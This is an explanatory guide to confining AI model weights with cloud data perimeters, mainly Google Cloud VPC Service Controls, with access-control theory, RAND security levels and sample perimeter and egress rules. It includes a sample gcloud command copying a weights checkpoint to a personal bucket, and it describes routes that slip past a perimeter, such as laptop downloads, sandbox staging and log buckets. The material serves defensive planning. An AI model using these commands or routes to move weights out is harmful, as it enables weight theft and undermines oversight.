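# Cloud data perimeters: stopping people who may read model weights from copying them to outside accounts

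## What a data perimeter does, and what confining weights would require

A cloud data perimeter is a set of organization-wide rules that limit which identities, resources and networks can be involved in a request to a cloud service, regardless of the permissions individual people hold. Organizations use perimeters mainly to keep data from being moved to places they do not control. Here, the data is model weights, the learned numbers that make up a trained AI model. Anyone with a copy can run the model without the developer's restrictions or monitoring. The weight files for the most capable models can total terabytes, and developers often store them with one of the large cloud providers: Amazon Web Services (AWS), Google Cloud or Microsoft Azure.

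Suppose an engineer at an AI company is allowed to read the model weights because her job is to test them. She opens her own cloud account, creates a storage area in it and lets her work identity write there. Using that identity, she then asks the cloud provider to copy the weights from the company's storage to hers. The provider checks whether she may read the source and write to the destination. The company granted the first permission and she granted the second, so the copy goes through unless the company has limited her writing to named locations. The copy can run entirely between the provider's machines, so the files never pass through her laptop or the office network, where monitoring software might have detected them.

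She has broken her employment contract, but no technical rule. A read permission determines who may open a file but doesn't restrict where its contents may go next.

### The cloud terms this depends on

Each provider divides its customers' resources into units. AWS uses accounts and Google Cloud uses projects, and a company groups either under an organization. On Azure, the outermost unit is the tenant, a company's directory of identities, with its subscriptions and storage beneath it. Below, "outside account" means any account, project or tenant that the company does not control, including the engineer's own.

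Weights are usually kept in object storage, which stores whole files in named containers (called buckets on AWS and Google Cloud) and serves them over the network. Unlike a disk in a server room, a bucket has no fixed place inside a company's network. Anyone with the right credentials can address any bucket the provider hosts, so writing to a stranger's bucket is as easy as writing to the company's.

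A principal is the human or machine identity that makes a request, such as an employee's or a training job's. A permission lets a principal perform some action on some resource. The system that stores and evaluates permissions is called identity and access management (IAM). A private network (called a virtual private cloud, or VPC, on AWS and Google Cloud) connects the customer's rented machines to each other, and the customer decides which routes lead out of it.

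A request to a cloud service, such as "copy this object to that bucket", specifies a principal, an action and a target, and the provider can test all of them against rules before it does anything. Traffic to the internet lacks this structure. If a program on a rented machine opens an encrypted connection to a file-sharing site, the provider's network carries bytes to an address, and no storage service checks who owns the destination.

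### What the perimeter adds

A data perimeter adds another check to the engineer's request. AWS's *Establish permissions guardrails using data perimeters* defines the goal as letting only trusted identities reach trusted resources from expected networks, where "trusted" mostly means owned by the company or by an AWS service acting for it. The engineer's work identity is trusted, but her bucket belongs to another organization, so the provider refuses the copy even though both permissions are in order. Google Cloud's VPC Service Controls draws a boundary called a service perimeter around chosen projects and services. Google gives almost the same example, in which a copy between two buckets succeeds if both are inside the perimeter and fails if one is outside.

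Both providers present the perimeter as an addition to permissions. Google says its version is independent of IAM, so a mistaken grant in one system does not by itself open the other. AWS calls its guardrails coarse-grained and warns that they do not replace decisions about who may read which data. A perimeter does not stop an employee who reads weights she does not need but keeps them inside it.

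Google Cloud also states that a service perimeter does not block third-party services on the internet. If an engineer loads the weights onto a rented machine and uploads them from there to a file-sharing site, the perimeter will not stop the upload. Google also did not design the product for comprehensive control of metadata, such as bucket names, so a claim that "the data cannot leave" covers only particular routes. The metadata gap matters less for weights, because moving a terabyte through bucket names is impractical.

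### Discretionary control, mandatory control and confinement

Computer scientists working on military systems faced a version of the engineer's case in the early 1970s. Their terms are still the best for describing what a perimeter would have to do.

Under discretionary access control, whoever owns a file decides who else may use it. Cloud permissions work largely this way. Its weakness is that anyone who can read a file can copy the contents into a new one, which they then own and can share as they choose. Under mandatory access control, a system-wide rule governs access, usually through labels on people and files, and users cannot waive it even for files they created.

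David Bell and Leonard LaPadula gave mandatory control its standard mathematical form in a series of reports for the US Air Force that began in 1973. Every subject (a user, or a program running for one) and every object (such as a file) has a security level. One rule covers reading: a subject may read an object only if the subject's level is at least as high as the object's. On its own this leaves the engineer's route open, because a person cleared for secret files could read one and write its contents into an unclassified file. So Bell and LaPadula added a second rule, the star property. If a subject can read object *a* and write to object *b* at the same time, then

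level(*a*) ≤ level(*b*).

Information may flow to the same level or a higher one, but never to a lower one. Suppose the cloud has two levels, 1 for everything the company owns and 0 for everything else. The rule then forbids the engineer from copying the weights to an outside account, because that would move them from level 1 to level 0.

A data perimeter partly resembles this two-level system. It attaches the level to the account or project that holds a bucket, rather than to the weights themselves. This makes little difference while the weights stay in company storage, but once they reach somewhere the rules do not cover, the file has no label that would make the next system restrict it. Bell and LaPadula also allowed for trusted subjects, which are exempt from the star property because somebody has established that they will not misuse the exemption. Every exception a company writes into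 its perimeter, for a business partner or for one of the provider's own services, creates something like a trusted subject, often without the same scrutiny.

The star property constrains only the reads and writes that the system recognizes as such. In *A Note on the Confinement Problem* (1973), Butler Lampson also considered leaks through other channels. He asked how a customer could run someone else's program on private data without letting the program pass the data to its author. Like the engineer, the program is allowed to read the data. It could write the data to a file its author can open, send a message to another program, or encode the data in the customer's bill. It could also speed up and slow down its use of the machine in a pattern that a cooperating program measures. Lampson called this last kind a covert channel, meaning one that was not designed to carry information. His simplest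 remedy was total isolation, in which a confined program may not call any other program. Where that is too strict, the system must also confine any untrusted program that a confined program calls.

James Anderson's *Computer Security Technology Planning Study* (1972), likewise written for the Air Force, had already proposed an enforcing mechanism called a reference monitor, which stands between subjects and objects and checks that every access is authorized. Anderson required the monitor to be tamperproof, to run on every access, and to be small enough to analyze and test completely.

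### Five tests

Together these ideas yield five tests for any arrangement that claims to confine weights.

1. The reader cannot lift the restriction. This is the difference between mandatory and discretionary control. If the engineer can mark her own bucket as trusted, or share a company bucket with an outside account, the arrangement fails.

2. Every path is checked. Anderson asked for this directly, and Lampson's list shows how long the inventory of paths can grow. Paths in a cloud include services that copy data as a side effect of some other job, as well as connections that never touch a cloud service. Very slow channels matter less for weights than for passwords, because the files are so large.

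3. The restriction follows copies and derived files. Under the star property, whatever a reader of secret files writes must itself be at least secret. Weights make this harder than documents do, since a useful derivative need not resemble the original. RAND (2024), in a study of weight theft by the US research organization, notes that models perform decently with each weight stored in only 4 bits, and that even a quarter of the weights of some models might provide dangerous capabilities. A rule tied to one file name or one bucket misses both.

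4. Those bound by the rules cannot change them. This comes from Anderson's ban on tampering. It differs from the first test because it concerns administrators, who may hold no special right over the weights and yet be able to rewrite the perimeter. Requiring a second person to approve such changes is the usual answer.

5. Enforcement can be verified. Anderson wanted a mechanism small enough to examine completely. Cloud customers cannot examine the provider's enforcement code, so they are left with reading their own rules, sending requests that ought to fail, and checking the logs. This is weaker evidence than Anderson had in mind.

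From here on, "mandatory confinement" means a restriction on where data may flow that no authorized reader can lift and that applies to every copy. The first and third tests define it, and the other three establish whether it holds in practice.

### Which insiders the defenses are meant to stop

Drawing on interviews with 32 experts, RAND compiled 38 ways of stealing weights, in nine categories. Several involve people authorized to read the weights. The human intelligence category includes bribery, extortion and placing trained candidates in sensitive jobs, and RAND notes that a recruiter need not reveal whom he works for. Extortion can begin with a request to copy one file, which the recruiter presents as minor and then uses as a threat. A thief who logs in with an engineer's stolen credentials has her permissions, and a perimeter treats the two of them alike. Authorized readers can also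 expose weights by mistake, and RAND attributes a large portion of insider risk to people who mean no harm.

The study then defines five security levels (SL1 to SL5) by the attackers a system should withstand. The right-hand column below lists what each level requires for copies and readers.

| Level | Attackers the system should likely thwart | Copies and readers |
|---|---|---|
| SL1 | Amateurs | Access control and an access log; the organization trusts employees to keep sensitive data on its systems |
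| SL2 | Professionals making opportunistic or moderate efforts | Weights only on servers; the organization prevents or searches for stray copies; insiders are outside the threat model |
| SL3 | Criminal syndicates and insiders | No direct read access to any copy, even for authorized users |
| SL4 | Standard operations by leading state cyber units | Weights on physically separate systems with hardware limits on output |
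| SL5 | Top-priority operations by the most capable states | A completely isolated network, except for production use |

The step from SL2 to SL3 matters most here. RAND bars direct read access at SL3 because it "enables trivial copying". It offers three substitutes: staff may use reviewed interfaces that are hard to abuse, run any code in an environment that caps how much data comes out, or work freely on an isolated network in a room that no storage device enters or leaves. Even the reviewed interfaces need care, because an engineer can collect all the weights by repeatedly calling a seemingly harmless function that returns one at a time.

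A data perimeter alone meets none of these requirements, because people can still read the weights. It is most useful when people have direct read access and the company can only control where the weights go, which is the situation SL3 is meant to eliminate. That situation appears to have been common at the time of the RAND study. RAND noted that many existing workflows, including popular software for debugging and for interpretability research (the study of how models work internally), gave full access to the weights and satisfied none of the three substitutes. A perimeter could also count toward SL3's separate requirement for two independent layers of security, but only if it would hold even with the other layer completely compromised.

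These levels are based on expert judgment, and the experts agreed on some points more than others. RAND found that they generally agreed that insiders are a significant source of risk but disagreed about how many people should have access to the weights. Some insisted on a number in the low tens, while others called such a cut unnecessary or infeasible. RAND suspected that standard cloud service cannot meet SL4's isolation requirements, and it judged SL5 impossible to achieve in 2024.

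Companies do not always try to stop the insiders whom SL3 covers. Anthropic's *Responsible Scaling Policy Version 2.2*, its voluntary policy on catastrophic risk, took effect on May 14, 2025. The policy's ASL-3 Security Standard, the company's third level of protection, included internal employees among the attackers it covered. A footnote defined "basic" insider risk as coming from someone without persistent or time-limited access to systems that process weights, and "sophisticated" insider risk as coming from someone who has persistent access or can request time-limited access. Anthropic committed to robust controls against basic risk but excluded sophisticated risk, along with state-compromised insiders. Before that amendment, the explicit exclusion had covered only "highly sophisticated state-compromised insiders", according to Anthropic's history of the policy.

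The labels are based on access rather than skill, which makes them easy to misread. The engineer with her credit card and personal bucket is a sophisticated insider, and so is a colleague who has never opened the weights but may ask to. Anthropic's *Frontier Model Security*, an older post, explains the practice behind the wording. Nobody keeps standing access to critical systems, and staff who need access ask a coworker for it, for a limited period and with a business reason. The size of the class depends on who may ask, which the definition leaves open.

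The exclusion means Anthropic does not claim that the standard as a whole should stop an authorized reader, but individual protections may still apply. In October 2024 Anthropic described plans for research tools that work without direct access to the weights, and for temporary access that requires a hardware key, a justification and an employee's approval. In its 2025 policy, it also promised further work on insider protections.

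Anthropic's *Responsible Scaling Policy Version 3.4* (2026), effective July 8, 2026, now separates what the company plans to do from what it recommends for the whole industry. Anthropic itself commits to maintaining or improving its ASL-3 protections, whose 2025 standard left out authorized readers. For the industry, it recommends that once AI systems can fully automate, or dramatically accelerate, research in fields such as AI itself, a developer should make a strong argument that even malicious insiders "with maximal levels of access", up to the chief executive, would gain no significant help in causing a catastrophe. Anthropic adds that this would likely require security roughly in line with SL4 against outside thieves, and that it cannot commit to the recommendations unilaterally.

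At that threshold, Anthropic itself plans to log all critical AI-development activities and have AI search the logs for, among other things, concerning behavior by insiders (including AI systems). Outsiders have little way to judge how far Anthropic's current controls already restrain an authorized reader, because the public version of its *Frontier Safety Roadmap* is redacted, partly to avoid telling attackers too much about those controls.

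## Mapping the copies of the weights and choosing the boundary

A company has to know where its weights are before it can draw a boundary around them. RAND points out that a thief needs only one poorly secured copy, however well the company protects the others. RAND considered five settings: training, research, the company's own use of the model, the public service, and sites where another organization runs the model itself. Each tends to accumulate copies, some of which people make by accident.

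### Where copies sit

The obvious copies are files in object storage. A long training run saves checkpoints so that it can restart after a failure. Each checkpoint contains the full weights at that moment, often with extra numbers that only the training algorithm needs, so it can be several times the size of the finished model. A late checkpoint would be almost as useful to a thief as the final weights. The finished weights go to a bucket, which may also keep earlier versions and recently deleted files. Backups and automatic replication to another region add more copies, and a backup can remain after the original is deleted.

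Other copies are easier to overlook because different permissions control them. For example, a test machine might download the weights to its disk. Anyone allowed to take a snapshot of that disk (a copy of its contents at one moment, stored by the provider) and attach it to another machine can then get the weights without permission to read the bucket. A machine image, which is a template for starting new machines, poses the same problem. Engineers sometimes build weights into a container image, which packages a program with everything it needs to run, and anyone allowed to download that image can get the weights. Container images are stored in registries, and many companies run a separate registry for trained models, which may hold its own copy.

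The machines that serve the model also hold copies of its weights. They often cache the weights on local disks so that they can restart quickly, and they must keep them decrypted in memory while the model runs. An administrator of the machine may be able to read that memory, and a crash can write it to a file that someone later collects for debugging.

For each copy, the company should record the project or account that holds it, who may read or duplicate it, why it exists and when to delete it. Asking each team will produce much of the list, and searching should turn up more copies. Access logs, where the company has switched them on, show which identities have read the weights bucket. Storage inventories show large files, but software often splits weights over many files, so the search has to add up the file sizes in each folder.

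The company also needs a list of the transfers that people's work requires. fwd:cloudsec's *Data Perimeters* (2026), the abstract of a talk at a cloud security conference, puts an inventory of existing traffic before any lockdown. Anthropic's *Activating AI Safety Level 3 Protections* (2025) reports that limiting the bandwidth out of the environments that hold weights forced Anthropic to understand how data was leaving its systems. A bandwidth limit can have this effect because a large transfer missing from the list will hit the limit.

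The next step is to delete most of the copies. RAND calls centralizing the copies a prerequisite for many other controls. At SL3, the level meant to stop insiders, RAND allows weights to be stored in a small number of centrally managed locations, and there may be separate copies for training, research and production. Each new full copy needs approval from several people, including a senior executive, and counts toward a limit set in advance.

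RAND also suggests limiting how many people have each kind of access at SL3: at most 20 who can copy the weights, 50 who can work directly with them on an isolated network, and 100 who can run their own code on them in an environment that caps its output. A company that relies on ordinary cloud permissions will find the limit of 20 hard to apply, because anyone who may read a file and write somewhere else can copy it. The company has to count everyone with both permissions toward the 20.

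### A worked example

Suppose a company stores a model with one trillion parameters at one byte each. The file is about 1 terabyte (TB) and sits in one bucket. The training, evaluation and serving environments all use it, and each has its own project or account and its own machine identity. A researcher is allowed to read the bucket and run tests in the evaluation environment. Like most of her colleagues, she can also write to a sandbox, a company project where staff try out new software.

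One outside partner, a testing firm, sends questions for the model and receives its answers and scores. It never receives the weights, which follows RAND's SL3 rule that no third-party service has access to them. A partner that ran the model itself would need its own copy outside the company's perimeter. Anthropic requires such partners to have security controls equivalent to its own, including audit logs, protections against insiders and approval for access to model deployments.

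A thief can take less than the full terabyte. At 4 bits per weight, the model shrinks to 500 gigabytes (GB), and a quarter of that is 125 GB. RAND advises assuming that the effective size is at most a tenth of the actual size, which here means 100 GB or less. A search for stray copies that flags only terabyte files would miss these smaller copies.

The table lists every transfer the company permits. The last two columns show whether each transfer crosses a boundary around the whole company and whether it crosses a narrower one around the weights bucket and the three environments.

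| From | To | What moves | Crosses company boundary | Crosses weights boundary |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Training | Weights bucket | Finished weights, 1 TB | No | No |
| Weights bucket | Training, evaluation, serving | Weights, 1 TB per load | No | No |
| Other company projects | Training, evaluation, serving | Code, software images, training data | No | Yes |
| Training, evaluation, serving | Other company projects | Logs and measurements | No | Yes |
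| Partner | Evaluation | Test questions | Yes | Yes |
| Evaluation | Partner | Answers and scores | Yes | Yes |
| Serving | Customers | Answers to their queries | Yes | Yes |

Only the data flows in the first two rows carry weights, and they cross neither boundary. The company therefore has no legitimate reason to let weights leave the narrower boundary.

### One boundary around the whole company

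AWS's *Perimeter overview* treats every identity and resource in the company's organization as trusted, so the standard boundary runs around the whole company. Google Cloud also recommends one large perimeter, which it says protects better against data theft than several smaller ones. A single perimeter also takes less work to run, because the team in charge mostly has to watch traffic between the perimeter and the internet. Google's version can be smaller than the whole company, since Google advises leaving out projects that neither hold nor use sensitive data.

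In the example, this boundary stops the researcher from copying the weights to her personal cloud account, but it doesn't stop her from copying them to the sandbox, because her identity, the sandbox's bucket and the network all belong to the company.

Suppose she makes that copy in March. In April she changes teams and loses permission to read the weights bucket, but the sandbox copy is still there. In May she starts a machine in the sandbox, which has an open internet connection so that staff can download public software, and uploads the weights to a file-sharing site. The perimeter blocks none of this, because the March copy stayed inside the company and the May upload was ordinary internet traffic rather than a request to a cloud service. Anyone else with access to the sandbox could have uploaded the copy, including someone who never had permission to read the weights bucket.

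In Bell and LaPadula's terms, the copy to the sandbox stays at level 1, so the star property allows it. To forbid it, the company has to put the weights bucket and its three environments at level 2 and leave the sandbox and the other projects at level 1.

The wide boundary needs few exceptions for the model itself. The two transfers with the partner each need one, and customers' queries and answers need an opening in the network. But the boundary also includes the rest of the company, and the sales and finance departments have outside partners who need exceptions too. Someone who copies weights into a sales project can then use one of those exceptions to send them outside.

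The wide boundary adds little to the researcher's daily work, but every team in the company has to work within it. Google Cloud recommends against it where programs need unrestricted internet access or services that its perimeter doesn't support. It also says that a company whose developers lack managed devices or known network addresses may be unable to write the exceptions those developers need. Google Cloud's *Best practices for enabling VPC Service Controls* warns that enabling the controls carelessly can cause an outage, and tells companies to repeat the process for each program they add.

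### A separate boundary for the weights

Google Cloud also describes a perimeter around only the projects that hold sensitive data. It recommends this design when those projects are few and well defined, and advises against it when many projects might contain such data. If a company hasn't yet centralized its weights, many of its projects might contain copies, so it has to inventory the copies before drawing this kind of perimeter.

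Google generally prefers one perimeter, apparently because it considers data protected as long as it stays inside the company. It makes an exception for companies that host several independent customers, saying each customer should have its own perimeter if moving data from one to another would count as theft. The same reasoning applies to moving weights into the sandbox.

On AWS, a company can group accounts into organizational units and use condition keys to check which unit or account owns the target of a request. AWS's *Best practices for a multi-account environment* recommends keeping production data in its own units. On Azure, the company can give the weights separate administrators and permissions within its existing tenant. Microsoft's *Resource isolation in a single tenant* recommends this where possible, but requires separate tenants if the company has "minimal risk tolerance for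 unauthorized access by tenant members". A company worried about insiders probably meets that condition.

Inside the narrower boundary, the researcher can still copy weights between the three environments wherever her permissions allow. The company can reduce this by denying her permission to create buckets, snapshots or images there, since she only needs to read the weights and run tests. Her test machine still needs a disk, so she will have at least one place to write a copy.

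This boundary needs exceptions for four kinds of transfer instead of two, because code and training data now have to cross it on the way in and logs on the way out. Google Cloud warns that managing traffic between perimeters can take considerable work, and advises against designs with multiple bridges, or links between perimeters. Some tools also have to move. According to Google Cloud's *Supported products and limitations*, Infrastructure Manager, a service that sets up cloud resources from written configurations, needs its service account, build machines and storage bucket in the same perimeter. A company that uses it on both sides would have to run it twice. Researchers would notice the boundary mostly when a program in another project could no longer open the weights.

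The exceptions for outgoing data need the most care. A rule that lets the evaluation environment write to a log bucket checks who is writing and where, but not whether the file contains logs. If the researcher can write to the bucket under this rule, she can copy weights there. The company should therefore limit the rule to a machine identity she cannot use, and investigate if a log bucket suddenly grows by 100 GB.

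The evaluation environment would send answers and scores for the partner to a release project outside the weights boundary, where a program would check their size and format before passing them on. The release project must have no permission to read the weights bucket. Google Cloud gives a similar example, in which a healthcare organization keeps identifiable records in one perimeter and puts de-identified data in another for sharing with outsiders.

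### A separate organization or tenant

The company could instead put the weights in a different AWS or Google Cloud organization, or a different Azure tenant, from the sandbox. The sandbox then counts as an outside account, so the rule that blocks copies to outside accounts covers it too. The researcher can still copy weights among the three environments.

A dedicated tenant mainly changes who runs the environment. Microsoft (2026) recommends one for critical systems when a company cannot accept the risk that remains in its main tenant. It has its own administrators and settings, and users can have separate accounts and devices for it. The company can also switch off collaboration with its other tenants. Microsoft mainly presents this as a way to contain break-ins and mistakes that begin elsewhere in the company, so it does less to stop a researcher whom the company has deliberately given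 access.

The same four kinds of transfer need exceptions, but those for code and logs now connect two organizations. Microsoft also lists duplicate licenses, separate monitoring and slower approvals among the drawbacks. AWS's *Multiple organizations* says most customers are best served by one organization for production and one for testing, because splitting work across more makes it harder to apply the same standards everywhere. Shared systems can also undo the separation. Microsoft warns that if both tenants copy their user accounts from the same company directory, an incident in that directory affects both.

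RAND's SL3 partly matches this option. It calls for a cloud network dedicated to sensitive data, such as AWS GovCloud (a separate part of AWS built for US government work) rather than standard AWS.

For the company in the example, a separate boundary for the weights is the best starting point on AWS and Google Cloud. It blocks the copy to the sandbox and lets the company keep a wider boundary around its other projects, but it requires two more kinds of exception. A separate organization becomes worthwhile if the main one has too many administrators for the company to trust them all with the weights. On Azure, a separate tenant is the better choice from the start by Microsoft's own criterion.

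## Setting up VPC Service Controls on Google Cloud

On Google Cloud, the company in the example can use VPC Service Controls to create the separate boundary around its weights. This boundary is a perimeter containing four projects, and a second perimeter contains the company's other projects. Google's rules identify projects by number, so the examples use these invented numbers.

| Project | Number | Location |
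|---|---|---|
| Weights bucket | 101 | Weights perimeter |
| Training | 102 | Weights perimeter |
| Evaluation | 103 | Weights perimeter |
| Serving | 104 | Weights perimeter |
| Release (checks scores before the partner gets them) | 201 | Company perimeter |
| Sandbox | 202 | Company perimeter |
| Testing partner's project | 801 | Partner's organization |
| Researcher's personal project | 901 | Outside account |

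### The parts of the configuration

Google Cloud's *Service perimeter details and configuration* starts with the access policy, which contains an organization's perimeters and the conditions they place on clients. An organization has one organization-wide policy and can add narrower ones for individual folders (groups of projects) or projects.

The next step is the service perimeter, which is mainly a list of projects. Google Cloud accepts only projects from the organization that owns the perimeter, so the partner's project can never be a member. Each project can belong to only one perimeter, so the weights perimeter can't sit inside a larger one around the whole company. The two are separate, and a request from one to the other has to satisfy the rules of both.

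Google decides whether a machine is inside a perimeter by looking at the project that owns the machine's network, which may not be the project that owns the machine. When several projects share a network, Google Cloud's *Troubleshoot common issues* requires the project that hosts it to be in the same perimeter as the projects connected to it. If the sandbox shared a network with the evaluation environment, the sandbox's machines could count as inside the weights perimeter. The four weights projects should therefore have a network of their own.

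The engineer then lists the services to protect, which Google calls restricted services. The perimeter covers only these, and every other service stays open to anyone with the right IAM permissions, as Kruiver explains in *VPC Service Controls*, a guide from the consultancy Xebia. Listing Cloud Storage alone would leave out disk snapshots, machine images and container images, all of which can hold weights. It would also let a researcher load the weights onto a test machine and write them in pieces to an unlisted service in her own project. The safest list contains every service Google supports, including those the company doesn't use.

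A second list, called VPC accessible services, is easy to confuse with the first. The protected list governs requests that cross the perimeter, while this one limits what machines on the network may call at all, even within the perimeter. Google Cloud's *VPC accessible services* gives the example of a perimeter with data in both Cloud Storage and Bigtable, a database. If a thief steals a machine's credentials, the thief could take data from either, but if the list contains only Cloud Storage, the machine can't reach Bigtable. The list applies only to traffic from the company's network and has no effect on requests that one Google service sends to another. The company can set it to match the protected list, which gives this configuration:

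```yaml
name: accessPolicies/222/servicePerimeters/Weights
title: Weights
status:
  resources:
  - projects/101
  - projects/102
  - projects/103
  - projects/104
  restrictedServices:
  - storage.googleapis.com
  - compute.googleapis.com
  - artifactregistry.googleapis.com
  # plus every other supported service
  vpcAccessibleServices:
    enableRestriction: true
    allowedServices:
    - RESTRICTED-SERVICES
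```

With this configuration alone, nobody can read the weights from outside the perimeter, not even staff using Google's web console from their laptops. The remaining parts of the setup add exceptions.

An access level defines which clients are acceptable, using attributes such as IP address, device or location. The engineer can attach one to the perimeter to admit matching requests from the internet, but Google Cloud recommends an ingress rule instead because it gives finer control. If a project in one perimeter requests a protected resource in another, Google Cloud refuses the request, even if an access level would normally admit the client. An access level for the office network therefore doesn't let the sandbox read the weights bucket.

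An ingress rule admits requests from clients outside the perimeter. Its "from" block lists identities and the places they may connect from, which can be projects, networks or access levels. Its "to" block lists the services, methods and projects those clients may use. According to Google Cloud's *Ingress and egress rules*, the identity setting `ANY_SERVICE_ACCOUNT` admits machine identities from any organization, and `ANY_IDENTITY` admits even requests with no identity.

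An egress rule has the same two blocks and covers requests that involve something inside the perimeter and a resource outside it. It can also restrict where requests come from, but only if the engineer sets `sourceRestriction` to `SOURCE_RESTRICTION_ENABLED`. Without that setting, Google ignores the list of sources and applies the rule wherever the request comes from.

"Ingress" and "egress" here refer to the direction of the request, regardless of which way the data moves. When a client outside the perimeter downloads a file from a bucket inside, Google counts that as ingress. So a company with no egress rules can still lose its weights through an ingress rule that permits downloads.

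### The restricted address range

The last part concerns the addresses that machines use to reach Google's services. By default, machines use Google's ordinary addresses. Google Cloud's *Configure Private Google Access* says these addresses lead to most Google services, including Gmail and Google Docs, whether or not VPC Service Controls supports them. If a test machine can reach these services, the researcher has another place to upload weights.

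The restricted range, 199.36.153.4/30, contains the four addresses from 199.36.153.4 to 199.36.153.7. Google doesn't announce it to the internet. It gives access to the services that a perimeter can protect and, according to Google Cloud, to several others that those services depend on. Google Cloud's *Configure Private Google Access for on-premises hosts* recommends the range as extra protection against data theft because it denies access to other unsupported services.

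Setting it up takes three changes to the network:

1. The engineer changes the network's name lookups so that Google's service names lead to the range. Google Cloud's *Private Google Access with VPC Service Controls* maps `*.googleapis.com` to `restricted.googleapis.com`. Container images in Artifact Registry use a different name, `*.pkg.dev`, which needs its own entry.

2. She adds a route to 199.36.153.4/30. Google Cloud's *Set up private connectivity to Google APIs and services* also lists a separate range, 34.126.0.0/18, for services that allow direct connections.

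3. She adds firewall rules that block other destinations. Name lookups only tell a program which address to use, and a program that already has another address can ignore them.

The firewall rules have to be exact, because a rule that allows 199.36.153.0/28 would also cover the neighboring range, 199.36.153.8/30. That range belongs to `private.googleapis.com`, which gives access to most Google services, whether or not a perimeter can protect them.

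Google Cloud's *Set up a VPC Service Controls perimeter for a Virtual Private Cloud* describes an alternative setup. The customer gives the supported services an address inside their network, points Google's service names to that address, and blocks all other outgoing traffic with a low-priority firewall rule.

### How Google decides one request

Suppose the researcher is logged in to a test machine in the evaluation project. She has created a bucket in her personal project and allowed her work identity to write to it. She runs this command:

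```
gcloud storage cp gs://company-weights/checkpoint gs://her-bucket/
```

The permissions on both buckets allow the copy, because the company lets her read the source and she has given herself write access to the destination. The perimeter adds a separate check, which depends on four facts.

- The service is Cloud Storage, which is on the protected list.
- The request comes from the network of project 103, inside the perimeter.
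- The source bucket belongs to project 101, inside, and the destination to project 901, outside.
- The identity is her work account.

Because the request involves both a protected project and an outside one, it needs an egress rule that matches the service, the method, the identity and project 901. No such rule exists, so Google refuses the copy with a 403 error and the message "Request violates VPC Service Controls." Owning project 901 doesn't help her, because the rule would have to be in the company's access policy, which only the company's administrators can edit.

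Google Cloud describes almost the same case, in which someone tries to move a file from a protected bucket to an outside one. The move fails whether the machine is inside or outside the perimeter, but Google logs different reasons. Google stops the machine inside when it tries to reach the outside bucket, and logs `NETWORK_NOT_IN_SAME_SERVICE_PERIMETER`. The machine outside passes that check but fails the next one, which Google logs as `RESOURCES_NOT_IN_SAME_SERVICE_PERIMETER`. For the machine inside, the log also records the method as `BillingRequiredRead`, so an investigator who searched only for writes would miss the attempted move. These sample logs date from 2018, so current entries may look different.

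Now suppose she tries to copy the checkpoint to a bucket in the evaluation project instead. The network and both buckets are in the same perimeter, so the request needs no rule and depends only on her permissions, which allow it.

The table adds some variations. In each one, IAM allows what she is trying to do.

| What the researcher tries | Rules the request needs | Result |
|---|---|---|
| Copy from the weights bucket to an evaluation bucket, on the test machine | None | Succeeds |
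| Copy from the weights bucket to her personal bucket, on the test machine | Egress to project 901 | Fails |
| Save the weights to the test machine's disk, then upload them to her personal bucket | None for the first step, egress to project 901 for the second | The upload fails |
| Copy from the weights bucket to her personal bucket, on her laptop | Ingress for the laptop and egress to project 901 | Fails |
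| Download the weights to her laptop, then upload them to her personal bucket | Ingress for the first step, none for the second | Succeeds if any ingress rule or access level permits the download |

The last row is the dangerous one. Once the weights are on the laptop, Google won't apply the company's rules to the upload, because the laptop and the destination bucket are both outside the perimeter. A company that wants its researchers to work from their laptops should let them manage test machines in project 103 but give them no ingress rule for reading Cloud Storage. They can then read the weights only from machines inside the perimeter. This is somewhat less convenient, since tools that browse buckets from a laptop will stop working.

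The perimeter also covers some copies that a Google service makes on a user's behalf. An insider who can't copy a file directly might try these indirect routes, but for supported services the same egress check applies. Google Cloud describes a data-processing job that reads a file inside the perimeter and fails when writing the result to a bucket outside. If an administrator has set up automatic log exports from a protected project to an outside one, those exports also fail, because the logging service makes the request under a service identity and Google treats it as coming from the protected project.

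### An egress rule for the testing partner

The partner receives answers and scores from the release project, which has no permission to read the weights. This rule goes in the company perimeter:

```yaml
- title: Scores to testing partner
  egressFrom:
    identities:
    - serviceAccount:score-release@release-project.iam.gserviceaccount.com
    sources:
    - resource: projects/201
    sourceRestriction: SOURCE_RESTRICTION_ENABLED
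  egressTo:
    resources:
    - projects/801
    operations:
    - serviceName: storage.googleapis.com
      methodSelectors:
      - method: google.storage.objects.create
      - method: google.storage.Write
```

The rule lets one machine identity, working from the release project, create files in the partner's project. Its methods come from Google Cloud's *Secure data exchange with ingress and egress rules*, which uses them in a rule for sharing anonymized health records. Google's version uses `ANY_IDENTITY`. Here that would let anyone with access to the release project's files copy them to any bucket in project 801 where the partner had given that person write permission, which a researcher could arrange through a friend at the testing firm.

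The release project can't send anything until it receives the scores from the evaluation environment, which is in the weights perimeter. That transfer requires an egress rule in that perimeter and a matching ingress rule in the company perimeter. Both rules should specify project 201 and a machine identity that researchers can't use. If the partner has its own perimeter, that perimeter also needs an ingress rule.

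The partner's test questions need a separate rule. The partner can keep them in its own bucket, and a program in the release project can read them with `google.storage.objects.get`. This read also counts as egress, although the data is coming in. A rule limited to that method doesn't let the program write to the partner's bucket.

The rule for sending scores doesn't check what a file contains, so the release program has to do that. The rule also applies to a whole project, because Google's rules can't single out a bucket by name or label. If the partner later uses project 801 for other work, the company's exception will also cover the buckets for that work, without anyone at the company changing it.

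### Perimeter bridges

A perimeter bridge is an older way to connect projects in different perimeters. The engineer names the projects, and Google then lets each one make requests to the others' services. Google Cloud's *Sharing across perimeters with bridges* says that data can move in both directions and that a company wanting to control the direction should combine the bridge with IAM permissions. Kruiver says that a bridge defeats the purpose of the perimeter between the bridged projects, leaving only IAM to control access.

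The company can't use a bridge for the partner, because all bridged projects must belong to the same organization. It could use one between evaluation and release, but then a program in the release project could read any checkpoint left in an evaluation bucket, if IAM allowed it, and a researcher could copy weights into a release bucket. The pair of rules described above permits only files that the one machine identity writes, which are meant to be score files but could be any file.

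A perimeter bridge makes sense when two projects in the same organization hold equally sensitive data, use many of each other's services in both directions, and need no control between them beyond IAM. None of the transfers into or out of the weights perimeter meets those conditions. Code comes in and logs go out through a few known services, so the company should write ingress and egress rules for those transfers and use bridges only in other parts of the business.

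With a bridge, each project can reach any new bucket in the other as soon as someone creates it, without a change to the perimeter. A chain of bridges can also let people move data further than its designers intended. If projects A and B share a bridge, and B and C share another, Google Cloud blocks direct requests between A and C. But someone with access to all three could copy a file from A to B and then from B to C, since each step is allowed.

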